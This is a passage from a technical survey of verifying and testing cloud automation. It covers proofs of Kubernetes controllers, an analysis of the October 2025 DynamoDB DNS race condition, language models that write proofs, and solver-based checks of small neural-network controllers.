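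The proof assumes that the model of the cluster is accurate, that the team correctly defined "always" and "eventually" when adding them to Verus, and that Verus, Z3, the Rust compiler and the operating system work correctly. Anvil and the three controllers together contain about 10,100 lines of trusted code, compared with 3,940 lines of verified executable code, but about two-thirds of the trusted lines are simple wrappers around Kubernetes data types. The model of the environment has 1,846 lines, and a mistake there would be harder to spot.

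Kubernetes' built-in StatefulSet controller repeatedly writes status information into the same object that the ZooKeeper controller needs to update. When both try at once, only one succeeds, so the ZooKeeper controller's update could in theory fail every time. One of the model's assumptions is that the built-in controller eventually pauses until the other update gets through. The model does not include custom controllers that a company might run to edit the same objects, so the proof does not rule out conflicts with them.

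The definition of "match" is narrower than a user might expect. For ZooKeeper, it requires the right objects to exist in the data store with the right contents, including a stateful set with the requested number of replicas. Kubernetes' own controllers, which are unverified, are then responsible for starting that many working servers.

The bug in the ZooKeeper interface fits a pattern from earlier research. Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues (2017), in *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems*, examined three such systems, IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar, and found 16 bugs:

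| Location | Bugs |
|---|---|
| Shim layer, the unverified code that connects the verified part to the network and operating system | 11 |
| Verification tools | 3 |
| Specifications | 2 |
| Verified protocols | 0 |

Verdi's shim layer, for example, assumed that one network read would return a client's whole request, so a request that arrived in pieces could crash the server. Two of the bugs in the verification tools were more worrying in principle, because they could make a tool accept an incorrect program.

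Fonseca and colleagues found no protocol bugs, even though they spent more than eight months on the search and looked specifically for them. That is impressive, because such bugs are common in mature unverified systems. Three research prototypes are a small sample, but the result suggests that proofs work well where they apply and that testers should concentrate on the boundary of what the proofs cover. The test toolkit that the team built for this purpose detects 13 of the 16 bugs.

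### Cheaper checks: Kivi and Sieve

Anvil works only for controllers written or rewritten in its style, and companies already run thousands of others. *Who Watches the Watchers?* (Gu, Tang and colleagues, 2026) analyzes 412 real-world failures from just thirteen of these. Two other methods take less work and apply to existing controllers.

Kivi, the model checker introduced earlier, looks for failures that arise when controllers run together under a particular configuration. One of its test cases has three machines, two in one zone and the third in another. The user wants six replicas and requires that the number of replicas differ by at most one between any two machines, and by at most one between the two zones. Meeting the machine limit takes two replicas on each machine, but that puts four in one zone and two in the other, which breaks the zone limit. Kubernetes therefore places five replicas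 and cannot place the sixth. A proof about the controller's code would not have prevented this, because the code did what the settings required.

In another case, two controllers conflict. The scheduler, which assigns replicas to machines, spreads them evenly only as a preference, while the descheduler, which removes badly placed replicas, enforces even spreading as a requirement. The descheduler removes a replica, a third controller creates a replacement, the scheduler puts it back in the wrong place, and the cycle repeats indefinitely.

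Kivi checks most of its test cases within 100 seconds and all of them within 25 minutes, but it can miss failures. Its models cover only the main logic of six controllers, so it can't find bugs in any other code. It also checks clusters only up to a limited size, which Liu and colleagues set at six machines, twice the most that any failure in their collection needed. But the collection contains only failures that people had already noticed and understood. A failure that needs twenty machines would exceed Kivi's limit, and might be missing from the collection because its size kept people from noticing or understanding it. Liu and colleagues acknowledge that their approach may not suit problems that depend on proportions. The loss of one machine in fifty can go unnoticed while the problem slowly spreads, whereas someone notices immediately when one in three fails.

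Sieve runs a controller's real code and disturbs its view of the cluster. It detects bugs by comparing how the cluster's state develops with and without the disturbance (Sun, 2025, *Verification and Testing of Cloud Infrastructure Systems*). The undisturbed run replaces a specification, so the method is easy to apply to many controllers. Sieve found 46 bugs, of which developers had confirmed 35 and fixed 22 (Sun, Luo and colleagues, 2022, *Automatic Reliability Testing For Cluster Management Controllers*). Only 3.5% of its reports were false alarms.

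Sieve covers only the situations that its tests create. Extensive testing with Sieve missed the crash bug that the Anvil team later reported in the reference ZooKeeper controller, because the bug appears only with a particular timing and workload. Comparing two runs also cannot reveal a mistake that occurs in both. Sun, who led the work on both Sieve and Anvil, still argues that testing is necessary until verified replacements exist, and that it can catch bugs in the interaction between verified and unverified programs.

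### Several controllers at once

Anvil's published proofs each cover one custom controller. The project's description, copied in Ecosyste.ms' *Anvil* in May 2025, lists the same three verified controllers and mentions work on more, including some of Kubernetes' built-in ones. Proofs about how verified controllers interact were still planned when the 2024 paper was published.

*KUBEDIRECT* uses TLA+ to check a whole chain of controllers. One property it highlights is that if something is true at the lower end of the chain, such as "this replica runs on that machine", it eventually becomes true in the records of every controller above. The paper calls this a safety invariant, but the word "eventually" makes it a liveness property by Alpern and Schneider's definition. The check covers only the design, and the code can diverge from it.

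*Garen* (2026) instead changes the cluster manager so that each reconciliation is atomic, meaning it takes effect completely or not at all. The paper also studies 51 consistency bugs in Kubernetes controllers, many of which were still unresolved. Kubernetes developers often rejected proposed fixes because the changes would break existing software or slow the system down.

### Proofs written by AI

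Language models can now do much of the proof writing. For *VeruSAGE-Bench*, Yang, Hawblitzel and colleagues (2025) took 849 functions from eight verified Rust projects, including Anvil, removed the proofs and had models write new ones. The best model they tested, Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5, succeeded on 94% of the tasks, at an average cost of about $14 each. It completed every task from Anvil's library of temporal lemmas and 83% of those from one of Anvil's Kubernetes controllers.

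In these tasks, the models could use the intermediate lemmas that human experts had stated, but not the proofs of those lemmas. When Yang and colleagues removed the lemmas, Opus 4.5 proved only 41% of the controller tasks, at $96 each. On one controller task it spent more than $500 and still failed.

Controller proofs are hard mainly because someone has to invent the invariants they require. For example, the number of RabbitMQ replicas never decreases, but checking each step separately cannot prove this, because a request to lower the number might already be in the network. The Anvil team first had to prove another invariant, that the network never contains such a request. Learned models in 2025 were poor at finding these stronger invariants.

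The more recent *KVerus* (2026) describes a tool that uses language models to write proofs inside existing Rust projects. The tool produced 21% of the proof code for CortenMM, an operating-system memory manager, and succeeded on 51% of tasks set in complete projects.

In *Extending concurrent separation logic to the hardware level*, Kaashoek and Zeldovich (2026) verified xv6, a small Unix-like operating system kernel, with the help of AI agents. The work took 102 days, including the time to build their verification framework. The kernel has 6,657 lines of source code and the proof has about 1.6 million, or roughly 240 lines of proof per line of code. Kaashoek and Zeldovich did not need to read the proof, because a proof checker verified it. The proof-to-code ratios for Anvil's controllers are therefore no longer a good measure of effort.

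Kaashoek and Zeldovich still planned the framework, helped design the specifications, and wrote instructions for the agents that were about three times as long as their paper. They also proved only safety properties. For example, they proved that when a user types a command to print "hello world", only that text or one of several listed errors can appear on the screen. A system that printed nothing would satisfy this theorem. They tested separately that the kernel does print the text. It is still an open question whether agents could produce a liveness proof such as Anvil's at this scale.

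Even when proofs take less work to write, their trusted parts must still be checked by other means. Yang and colleagues did not test whether models can write specifications, and they point out that a verifier cannot determine whether a specification matches what its user wants. The xv6 project found 11 bugs in the kernel and one in the official formal model of the RISC-V processor, which is part of the proof's trusted base.

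## A fault in automation that had no formal model: the DynamoDB outage of October 2025

Few automation programs have proofs like Anvil's, and many have no formal model. On the night of 19 October 2025, a timing fault in one of these programs cut off DynamoDB, AWS's database service, in the Northern Virginia region. Many other AWS services depend on DynamoDB and failed with it. Thousands of websites and apps also failed, according to *What caused the large AWS outage?* (Gergely, 2025). AWS published an explanation three days later, and Craig Howard, an engineer on the DynamoDB team, gave a more detailed one at the company's re:Invent conference in December.

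### The Planner, the Enactors and their plans

To use DynamoDB, a program first looks up a name, dynamodb.us-east-1.amazonaws.com, in the domain name system (DNS). The lookup returns the numerical address of a load balancer, a machine that spreads requests over the servers behind it. Without that address the program cannot connect, even if the database is working. Each region has hundreds of load balancers, and their capacity changes often, so software keeps the DNS records up to date.

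AWS's *Summary of the Amazon DynamoDB Service Disruption* (2025) describes this software as two components. The Planner monitors the load balancers and periodically writes a plan that lists which of them should receive traffic and what share each should get. The Enactor reads the latest plan and applies it in Route 53, AWS's DNS service. The plan is a desired state, and the Enactor is a controller. Three Enactors run independently in separate groups of data centres, so that updates continue if one fails.

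Kazuya's *AWS re:Invent 2025* is a machine-generated transcript of Howard's talk. The times it gives match those in AWS's summary, and its main statements about formal modelling match Lorin Hochstein's account of the talk in *aws reinvent talk on their oct 25 incident* (Surfing Complexity, 2025).

As Howard described it, an Enactor builds a complete new set of records for the new plan and then changes one top-level record to point to that set, rather than editing the records that customers are using. It does this for each endpoint, a name customers use to reach DynamoDB. The old sets remain for a while, so an operator can undo a bad plan by pointing the top-level record back. To keep old sets from piling up, an Enactor deletes those from much older plans after it finishes installing a plan.

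Two safeguards coordinate the Enactors. Before starting a plan, an Enactor checks once that the plan is newer than the one last applied. It also needs a lock on each endpoint before changing it. Other AWS teams keep such locks in DynamoDB, but this software might have to restore DynamoDB, so the team made the lock a DNS record containing its owner's name and an expiry time. If the lock is taken, the Enactor waits and tries again. The lock prevents two Enactors from changing an endpoint at the same time, but they can still change it in the wrong order.

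### How an old plan emptied the record

Howard illustrated the failure with made-up plan numbers. In the following version, A is the delayed Enactor, B is a faster one, and plan 109 is active at the start.

1. A picks up plan 110, checks that it is newer than 109, and begins to work through the endpoints.
2. A fails to get a lock several times in a row and waits after each attempt. Meanwhile, the Planner produces plans 111 to 145.
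3. B picks up plan 145, checks that it is newer than the last plan applied, and installs it at every endpoint. Plan 145 is now active.
4. B starts its clean-up, which will delete all plans much older than 145.
5. A finally gets the lock for the main regional endpoint and installs plan 110 there. It does not repeat the check from step 1, which would now fail.
6. B's clean-up deletes plan 110 because of its age. The endpoint now points to records that no longer exist.

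From then on, a DNS lookup for the endpoint returned no error and no address.

The team had anticipated parts of this sequence. An Enactor might install a slightly outdated plan, but that would do no harm because another Enactor would soon replace it with a newer one. Deleting very old plans is also harmless as long as they are not in use. The team had not anticipated that an Enactor could fall so far behind that its plan was old enough to delete. AWS's summary mentions only "unusually high delays", which Howard said was too vague. Enactors often compete for a lock, and the team expected the losses to be spread evenly, but this time one Enactor lost repeatedly.

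The six steps violate a safety property, the invariant that the active plan is never deleted.

### Why the automation could not repair itself

Howard said that if this had been the only defect, the outage would still have been large, but the system would have recovered very quickly. The Enactors were still running and the Planner was still producing plans, so the next installation should have filled the empty record.

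The next installation failed because of a feature meant to speed up recovery. Whenever an Enactor changes the top-level record, it also updates a rollback record, which points to the previously active plan so that an operator can return to it. Both changes belong to one transaction, so either both take effect or neither does. After step 6, the previously active plan was plan 110, which had been deleted. The code could not handle a rollback record that pointed to nothing, so the transaction failed for every Enactor and every new plan.

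Computer Enhance's *dynamodb dont leave me hanging* describes this as puzzling. The obvious implementation would read the current value of the top-level record, copy it into the rollback record and write the new value. None of these steps requires the old plan to exist.

The rollback fault violates the liveness property that whenever the endpoint's record is empty, the automation eventually fills it again. Each failed transaction leaves the state unchanged, so the system can repeat the attempt forever. In the outage, the loop ended only because people intervened, and their repair took longer because many of their tools relied on a working Enactor.

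The record was empty from 11:48 p.m. Pacific time until 2:25 a.m., and customers could reconnect by 2:40 a.m., as the empty answers stored in DNS caches expired. The wider disruption lasted until 2:20 p.m. Much of it came from EC2, the service that rents out virtual machines. EC2's management software depends on DynamoDB to renew a lease on each physical server every few minutes. When DynamoDB returned, so many leases had lapsed that renewals timed out before they finished, and each timeout added another attempt to the queue. Engineers had no established procedure for this, but eventually limited incoming work and restarted parts of the software. This was an overload failure, a kind that Brooker and Desai say does not fit neatly under safety or liveness. Proving the DNS automation correct could have removed the trigger, but the proof would not have covered EC2's recovery.

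AWS switched off the DNS automation worldwide that morning, because the same race could have occurred in any region. Existing records kept working without it. The team had fixed the race by 22 October and had the automation running again in every region by 28 October.

### The Spin and TLA+ models

Within days, people outside Amazon had reproduced the race from the published summary. In *Reproducing the AWS Outage Race Condition with a Model Checker*, Younas (2025) modelled one Planner and two Enactors in Spin, a model checker for concurrent programs. Each Enactor takes a plan from a queue, notes which plan is currently active, checks its own plan against that note, applies the plan and cleans up. The fault is possible because the note can be out of date by the time the Enactor applies the plan.

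Younas first wrote a more complicated invariant and then, after rereading AWS's summary, a direct one:

□(current_plan > 0 ⇒ ¬plan_deleted[current_plan])

In words, no active plan has been deleted. Both invariants fail in essentially the same way. In the counterexample, the faster Enactor applies plan 4 and deletes plans 1 and 2, but keeps plan 3 because it is too recent to delete. The slower Enactor then applies plan 3. When the faster Enactor resumes its clean-up, it deletes plan 3, which is now active. Spin reported the first violation after storing about 23,000 states, which is a very small search.

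In *TLA+ Modeling of AWS outage DNS race condition*, Demirbas (2025) asked ChatGPT to translate Younas's model into TLA+. The translation treated an Enactor's whole job as one indivisible step, which removed the race. The race returned when Demirbas split the job into three steps: receive a plan, apply it, and clean up. The table shows how the fault then arises if an Enactor's clean-up deletes plans at least two versions older than the one that Enactor has just applied.

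| Step | Active plan | Deleted plans |
|---|---|---|
| Enactor 1 receives plan 1 | none | none |
| Enactor 2 receives plan 2 and applies it | 2 | none |
| Enactor 2 cleans up | 2 | none |
| Enactor 2 receives plan 3 and applies it | 3 | none |
| Enactor 1 applies plan 1 | 1 | none |
| Enactor 2 cleans up | 1 | 1 |

In the single-step version, no other Enactor can act between applying a plan and cleaning up. The plan an Enactor has just applied is therefore still active during its clean-up, which deletes only older plans. A deleted plan cannot become active later, because an Enactor in the model cannot apply one. The invariant holds in every reachable state, so a model checker will correctly find no error. But this result does not cover the real system, where another Enactor can act between the two steps.

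Choosing a step size makes an assumption about the real system, often without the modeler noticing. Treating a piece of work as one step is safe only if nothing else can act partway through it, or if such an action would make no difference. Route 53's transactions justify this for a change to one endpoint, but not for the whole sequence of checking a plan, applying it to many endpoints and cleaning up. Anvil avoids the problem by building a limit of one request per step into the code.

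Smaller steps make the search larger. If two Enactors each handle one plan, single-step jobs can happen in 2 orders and three-step jobs in 20. With three Enactors, single-step jobs can happen in 6 orders and three-step jobs in 1,680. Engineers therefore have a good reason to merge steps, but if they merge too many, the search misses a bug without warning.

Both public models leave out much of the real system, including locks, retries and all but two Enactors. This hardly matters for the race, because a model checker lets any process pause for any length of time, whatever the cause. Both models also omit the rollback record, because AWS's summary had said only that the system was left in an "inconsistent state". This omission matters more, because without the record neither model could be used to find why the automation stayed stuck.

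The models are also a poor guide to why Amazon built the system as it did. Demirbas says Amazon separated the steps for performance, but Howard said the team did not care how many updates the Enactors could process and ran three of them only for reliability. Younas repaired his model by making the critical statements indivisible, which takes a few words in Spin. In the real system, the same repair would probably require a lock covering all endpoints, which the team had considered and rejected as too complicated.

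### Amazon's own model and the drift of the code

Amazon already had experience with these methods. According to slides from AWS (2023), the company had more than 100 TLA+ models in its code repositories, and DynamoDB was among the services that had them. Brooker and Desai, writing a few months before the outage, also name DynamoDB among the teams that use P, a modelling language designed to be easier for programmers. But Howard said the DNS automation had no formal model. The DynamoDB team had modelled other things, in particular the protocol that keeps copies of customers' data consistent.

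DNS updates presumably seemed simpler than that. In hindsight, Howard described the Enactors as running a consensus algorithm in disguise, because several independent programs had to agree on one active plan. Consensus algorithms are notoriously easy to get wrong, and an engineer who had recognised one here would probably have wanted a model.

After the outage, the team built a formal model in TLA+ to validate the fix. The engineers started with a description of the algorithm, drawn from old design documents and code comments, then refined the model with Amazon Q, the company's AI assistant, which also helped them find invariants. When they checked the model, they found that the original design was correct. The race was in the running code, which had drifted from the design in small details over the years. Hochstein also attributes the race to later incremental changes.

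The engineers then gave Q the model and the source code that had been running on the day of the outage, and asked where the two differed. Some differences were harmless simplifications. For example, the model had a fixed queue of plans, whereas the real Planner keeps producing new ones. Others had led to the race. The engineers changed the code and repeated the comparison, and Q reported that the problem was gone. They relied partly on this result when they decided to switch the automation back on.

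Howard called the comparison "game changing", and he is right if it works reliably, because keeping a model in step with code has always been tedious. The evidence so far is one success, reported by an Amazon engineer about an Amazon product, in a case where the team already knew there was a race to find. A language model that lists differences may also miss some, and a reader can't tell from the list what is missing. Anvil proves that code and model agree, so it doesn't have this weakness, but it requires code written for the purpose.

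Language models made two other mistakes, and the one that was harder to notice was more dangerous. When the team gave Q three log files and asked what had caused the outage, it pointed to a failure at 6:49:33 UTC. The outage had begun at 6:48, so Q had found an effect of the outage rather than its cause. The engineers noticed the discrepancy immediately, and they could still use the answer to find where to look in megabytes of logs. ChatGPT's single-step translation produced a model that passed its check, and Demirbas knew that something was wrong only because he already knew about the race. Someone modelling a new system would not have had that knowledge.

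### Whether an earlier model would have helped

A week after the outage, a participant on the TLA+ mailing list suggested that TLA+ could have prevented it, since the DynamoDB team already used the language. One reply in the thread, *Will there be a lesson learned on AWS 2025 East-1 Outage* (2025), said that using TLA+ in DynamoDB does not mean checking everything with it. Someone would first have had to suspect a problem in the DNS records, and checking and then updating them in separate steps had worked well for a long time.

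A model checker could probably have found the race. The invariant is one line long, two Enactors and a handful of plans are enough to reproduce it, and model checkers search for the unlucky orderings that tests miss. Howard said that a unit test might run a million times without producing this sequence. Even if the test failed once, an engineer might run it again, see it pass and blame the test environment.

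But the model would have had to describe the code as it was in October 2025. Howard thought a model written at the beginning would not necessarily have helped, because it would have confirmed a design that was correct. This seems right, and it is a more serious limitation than the absence of a model. The usual remedy is to update the model along with the system. According to a passage from its 2022 paper quoted in the mailing-list thread, the DynamoDB team does this for its replication protocol by adding new features that affect the protocol to the specification and checking them with the model checker. This works if engineers recognise which changes affect the protocol. The changes to the DNS automation were small implementation details, and the people who made them may not have thought of them as design changes.

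Methods that examine the running code are more likely to catch drift. PObserve, which compares a system's logs with its specification, could have caught the code doing something the design forbade, but only after it happened. If the drift appeared only under rare timing, the first log to reveal it might have been from the night of the outage. Deterministic simulation, another method that Brooker and Desai describe, runs the real code on a simulator that controls the order of events and the length of delays. A test could hold one Enactor back for 35 plans, but an engineer would have to think of trying this or let the simulator explore many orderings at random.

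The rollback fault would have been even harder to find with a model of the original design. In a correct design, nothing deletes the active plan, so a model checker never reaches a state in which the plan is missing. It can therefore verify that the automation always recovers, even though it never tests recovery from that state. To expose the fault, an engineer would have had to add an event that the rest of the model rules out, such as the active plan disappearing without cause, and check that the Enactors still make progress. Anvil's liveness proofs similarly allow any starting state.

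Some of this could have come from a much quicker exercise. Entropic Thoughts' *AWS DynamoDB Outage Analysis* applies system-theoretic process analysis, a method from safety engineering, to AWS's description. The analyst lists every action the software can take and asks when it would be dangerous to take it, omit it, or take it too early or too late. The resulting table lists deleting an active plan as unsafe. The article estimates the effort at perhaps two hours. It warns against hindsight bias but shows some itself, since it covers only the components already known to have taken part in the outage.

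Unlike a model checker, this method does not find the sequence of steps that leads to the dangerous deletion, but an engineer who has written down the rule can enforce it without knowing that sequence. If the clean-up had checked, in the same transaction as the deletion, whether any endpoint was using the plan, it would not have deleted plan 110, and the next Enactor could have replaced that plan.

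## Verifying small neural networks that control networks and clusters

Engineers could explain the DynamoDB failure step by step because people had written the rules that the Enactors followed. Some experimental controllers use a trained neural network instead of hand-written rules. Reading the network's weights explains very little about its behavior, but a solver can still prove properties of the network if it is small enough.

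### Three learned controllers

A computer that sends data over the internet has to choose a sending rate. Traditional congestion control uses handwritten rules, such as halving the rate when packets go missing. Aurora, a research system, uses a neural network instead. The network receives three measurements for each of the last ten sending rates it chose:

- the latency ratio, which is the delay divided by the lowest delay seen so far
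- the latency gradient, which shows whether the delay is rising or falling
- the sending ratio, which is the number of packets sent divided by the number that arrived, so a value of 2 means that half were lost

The network outputs one number, and Aurora raises the rate if that number is positive, lowers it if negative, and leaves it unchanged if zero.

Pensieve chooses one of six bitrates for the next few seconds of an online video. Its inputs include recent download times and the amount of video in the player's buffer. DeepRM schedules jobs on a cluster. It receives current processor and memory use and a queue of jobs, and either starts one of the jobs or waits.

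All three networks were trained by reinforcement learning, without anyone specifying the right action for each state. During training, the network acts, receives a score for the result, and adjusts its weights (internal numbers) to raise future scores. Pensieve's score, for example, rewards high picture quality and penalizes pauses in playback.

These networks are tiny by current standards. *Verifying Learning-Augmented Systems* (Eliyahu, Kazak and colleagues, 2021) lists 13 learned controllers and similar systems, about half with fewer than 100 neurons. DeepRM has 20, Aurora 48 and Pensieve 384. They can be this small because experts chose a few meaningful measurements as inputs, whereas an image-recognition network has to extract features from raw pixels.

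### Turning a network into constraints

An invented network with three neurons is enough to show the method. Its inputs are *p*, the share of packets lost, and *u*, the throughput as a share of the best the link has achieved. Both lie between 0 and 1. Its output *y* is the change in the sending rate:

*h*₁ = ReLU(*p* − 0.2)

*h*₂ = ReLU(0.4 − *p*)

*h*₃ = ReLU(*p* + *u* − 1)

*y* = −*h*₁ + *h*₂ + 0.5*h*₃

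ReLU (rectified linear unit) replaces negative numbers with zero and leaves other numbers unchanged. The sender must slow down whenever it loses at least half its packets, that is, if *p* ≥ 0.5, then *y* < 0. As with access policies, the solver searches for a violation, here values with *p* ≥ 0.5 and *y* ≥ 0.

Each unit is either off and outputs zero, or on and outputs the sum inside the brackets. Once the state of every unit is fixed, the whole network is a linear formula, which is easy to check. Three units give 2³ = 8 combinations, and *n* units give up to 2ⁿ, which is about 280 trillion for Aurora's 48 units.

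Solvers avoid most of these cases by calculating bounds first. If *p* is between 0.5 and 1, then:

| Unit | Range of the sum | State |
|---|---|---|
| *h*₁ | 0.3 to 0.8 | always on |
| *h*₂ | −0.6 to −0.1 | always off |
| *h*₃ | −0.5 to 1 | undecided |

Only two of the eight cases remain. The solver can also use these ranges to bound the output. Since *h*₁ is at least 0.3 and *h*₃ is at most 1, *y* is at most −0.3 + 0.5 = 0.2. This bound is correct but too loose to prove the requirement, because it combines the value of *h*₁ at *p* = 0.5 with the value of *h*₃ at *p* = 1. The solver therefore splits the problem on the undecided unit:

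- If *h*₃ is off, *y* = 0.2 − *p*, which is at most −0.3.
- If *h*₃ is on, *y* = 0.5*u* − 0.5*p* − 0.3, which is at most −0.05, at *u* = 1 and *p* = 0.5.

The output is negative in both cases, so the requirement holds for infinitely many inputs. If training had produced the weight 0.8 instead of 0.5 in the last line, the solver would have found a counterexample at the same point, where *y* would be 0.1. Very high throughput would then make the sender speed up even while it was losing half its packets.

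*Verifying Deep-RL-Driven Systems* (Kazak, Barrett and colleagues, 2019) points out that such questions are decidable, meaning that a solver with enough time always reaches an answer. This is often not true of ordinary programs. But the problem is NP-complete even for simple networks. Running the network on a counterexample confirms it quickly, but every known algorithm for finding one, or ruling one out, takes exponential time in the worst case. The problem is hard because ReLU units can imitate logic. If *a* and *b* are each 0 or 1, then ReLU(*a* + *b* − 1) is 1 exactly when both are 1. A network can therefore encode a complicated logical puzzle, and finding an input that produces a certain output can be as hard as solving the puzzle.

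Practical solvers differ mainly in how they calculate bounds and split the problem into cases. Marabou, an SMT solver for neural networks, splits it much as in the example. General optimizers such as Gurobi represent the state of each undecided unit as a variable that must be 0 or 1. α,β-CROWN calculates bounds layer by layer on a graphics processor, discards every part of the problem in which the bounds already prove the property, and splits the rest. It won the latest annual contest for such tools, to which eleven teams submitted entries (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026, *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*). Eight teams had entered the year before (Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues, 2025, *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)*).

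### whiRL: checking several decisions in a row

A controller's decisions affect its later inputs. If Aurora sends faster, for example, the next measurements may show more delay or loss. Checking one decision cannot reveal that a controller gets stuck, so the solver has to consider a sequence of decisions. Kazak and colleagues built a first tool for this in 2019, and Eliyahu and colleagues developed it into a fuller platform, whiRL, which uses the Marabou solver.

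whiRL treats each possible input to the network as a state. Its user supplies the network and four further things:

- *I*, the states in which a run may start
- *T*, a relation that determines which states may follow which
- *B*, the bad states (for a safety property), or *G*, the good states (for a liveness property)
- *k*, the number of steps to examine

For a safety property, whiRL then asks the solver for states *x*₁ to *x*ₖ that satisfy

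*I*(*x*₁) ∧ *T*(*x*₁, *x*₂) ∧ … ∧ *T*(*x*ₖ₋₁, *x*ₖ) ∧ (*B*(*x*₁) ∨ … ∨ *B*(*x*ₖ))

whiRL uses bounded model checking, which searches all runs up to a fixed length. Each step of a run depends on the network's output, so whiRL makes *k* copies of the network and uses the transition relation *T* to connect each copy's output to the next copy's input. With *k* = 8, Aurora's 48 neurons become 384. For a network of *n* neurons, the worst-case search grows from 2ⁿ to 2ᵏⁿ cases.

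The relation *T* models the environment. For Aurora, it requires the history to shift by one place at each step and the newest entry to reflect the rate the neural network just chose. It does not model cables, routers or other senders. When *T* cannot describe the environment exactly, Eliyahu and colleagues make it allow every real step and some that could never happen. If the solver then finds no violation of a given length, the real system has none of that length either, but a counterexample may include an impossible step.

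To check a liveness property, whiRL searches for a loop that never passes through a good state. Pensieve needs a different method because one of its inputs is the number of pieces of video remaining, so no state repeats. Eliyahu and colleagues therefore check whether the controller can go a fixed number of steps without reaching a good state.

In the table below, "excellent conditions" means no packet loss and a delay within 1% of the minimum. "Heavy loss" means at least half the packets are lost while the delay stays near its minimum, which can happen when a router has little memory for queued packets.

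| System | Requirement | Reported result |
|---|---|---|
| Aurora | In excellent conditions, don't keep the same rate forever | No violation up to *k* = 10 |
| Aurora | In excellent conditions, eventually speed up | Violated at *k* = 2 |
| Aurora | Under heavy loss, slow down immediately | Violated at *k* = 1 |
| Aurora | Under continuing heavy loss, eventually slow down | No violation up to *k* = 8, then timeouts |
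| Pensieve | If downloads are fast, eventually choose more than the lowest quality | Violated for every *k* from 2 to 8 |
| Pensieve | If downloads are slow and the buffer is nearly empty, eventually choose the lowest quality | No violation for *k* from 2 to 8 |

In the first Aurora counterexample, the controller repeatedly lowers its sending rate on a perfect connection until it reaches the minimum, then stays there. This is worse than the second, in which the controller keeps its rate unchanged despite high and fluctuating packet loss. In Pensieve's counterexamples, videos of 12 to 36 seconds play at the lowest quality, except for an opening piece already downloaded, although the connection could support higher quality.

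DeepRM failed three of its four requirements, all within a single step. When the cluster was full, it tried to start a job instead of waiting, whether the queued jobs were small or large. Of the other two requirements, which concerned free resources, one held and one failed, but the paper's definitions and results are inconsistent about which.

Most checks took seconds. The fourth Aurora requirement took minutes for *k* from 4 to 6 and hours for *k* = 7 and 8. At *k* = 9, the solver reached its 24-hour limit.

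Eliyahu and colleagues also checked Aurora and Pensieve during training. Aurora satisfied the first and fourth requirements after a single training episode but never satisfied the other two. The researchers suspect that a network quickly learns to avoid the few situations that the reward severely penalizes, such as pauses in a video, while other requirements hardly affect its score. If so, more training with the same reward won't necessarily help.

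One of the favourable results was wrong. Yang, Zheng and Chen (2024), in *Verification and Interpretation-Driven Safe Deep Reinforcement Learning Framework*, checked the four Aurora requirements with their own tool and found a counterexample to the last one. They traced the error to whiRL's encoding of the property, and whiRL's developers confirmed the mistake. The solver's result was correct for the property as encoded, but the encoding didn't match the intended requirement. The new tool could also vary the numbers in a requirement to find where the result changes. Aurora was certain to slow down only when the sending ratio exceeded about 50, meaning that 98% of packets were lost.

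### From short runs to runs of any length

Bounded model checking covers only the first *k* steps of a run. A follow-up tool, whiRL 2.0, added two techniques for proving properties of runs of any length.

The first, k-induction, extends the invariant proof used earlier for the rolling update. For a neural network, the proof that every single step preserves the invariant often fails, because the solver begins from a harmless state that the real system could never reach. k-induction demands more before it allows a violation. It has two parts:

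1. No run violates the property in its first *k* steps.
2. Whenever *k* consecutive states satisfy the property, the next state does too.

Requiring *k* good states in a row excludes many impossible starting points. This suits controllers with a limited memory, such as Aurora, whose history after ten steps comes entirely from the run itself. A similar argument works for liveness. If the solver shows that no run contains *k* consecutive states that are not good, the controller reaches a good state at least once every *k* steps, however long it runs.

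The second technique is invariant inference, a search for an invariant that implies the desired property. With such an invariant, checking one step can replace checking a long chain of network copies. The search in whiRL 2.0 is only partly automatic. Using both techniques, the tool proved safety and liveness properties of network controllers that could not previously be verified.

### diffRL: checking whole regions

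Many of whiRL's requirements cover only a narrow set of situations. For example, "excellent conditions" allows latency ratios from 1.00 to 1.01, so a controller that passes might still fail at 1.02. Eliyahu and colleagues acknowledge that they chose such constants somewhat arbitrarily. *Analyzing Symbolic Properties for DRL Agents in Systems and Networking* (Zangooei, Weil and colleagues, 2026) describes the earlier work as checking individual points, and presents diffRL, a framework that checks whole regions. This slightly overstates the difference, since whiRL's heavy-loss requirements cover a wide range of sending ratios. But a requirement that names the correct action only makes sense in extreme situations, where everyone agrees what that action is.

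diffRL avoids naming the correct action by comparing two decisions of the same network:

∀*x* ∈ *X*, ∀*s* with *l*ᵢ ≤ *s*ᵢ ≤ *u*ᵢ: *f*(π(*x*), π(*x* + *s*)) ≤ *d*

Here *X* is a region of inputs, π(*x*) is the action that the network chooses for input *x*, and *s* is a small change to the input, with limits *l*ᵢ and *u*ᵢ on each component. The function *f* measures how the two actions differ, and *d* is the largest difference allowed. Zangooei and colleagues study two kinds of property:

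- **Robustness.** Every input may change by up to ε in either direction, and *f* is the absolute difference |π(*x*) − π(*x* + *s*)|. A small measurement error should not cause a large change in the action.
- **Monotonicity.** Only selected inputs change, and only in one direction. If measured throughput rises, for example, Pensieve should not choose a much lower quality. In this case *f* is π(*x*) − π(*x* + *s*), so only a drop counts.

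The solver receives two linked copies of the network. If the network chooses from a list of actions, diffRL generates a separate query for each forbidden pair. Pensieve has six quality levels, and Zangooei and colleagues forbid drops of three or more levels in response to better throughput, which gives six forbidden pairs: from level 6 to 3, 2 or 1, from 5 to 2 or 1, and from 4 to 1. If the solver shows that none of the six can occur, the property holds throughout the region. The tolerance is generous, since a drop of two levels would still pass.

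The tests covered two versions of Pensieve, with 27,142 and 103,174 parameters, and gave two solvers a limit of 600 seconds per question. The solvers answered most questions when each input could vary over the middle 60% or 80% of its range, but many questions timed out when inputs could vary over the full range. The smaller network produced about 45% fewer timeouts and performed almost as well in training. For the larger network, only one of the two solvers finished in time on about 60% of the answered questions.

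The most striking counterexample came from CMARS, a neural network that divides radio capacity among groups of mobile users. In a lightly loaded system, changing the inputs by no more than 0.001, on a scale from 0 to 1, raised the capacity it assigned to one group from 3 units to 29. Random testing could easily miss such a jump. Adding a layer to CMARS did not reliably make it safer. With 15 possible actions, the deeper version had more violations and more timeouts than the shallower one.

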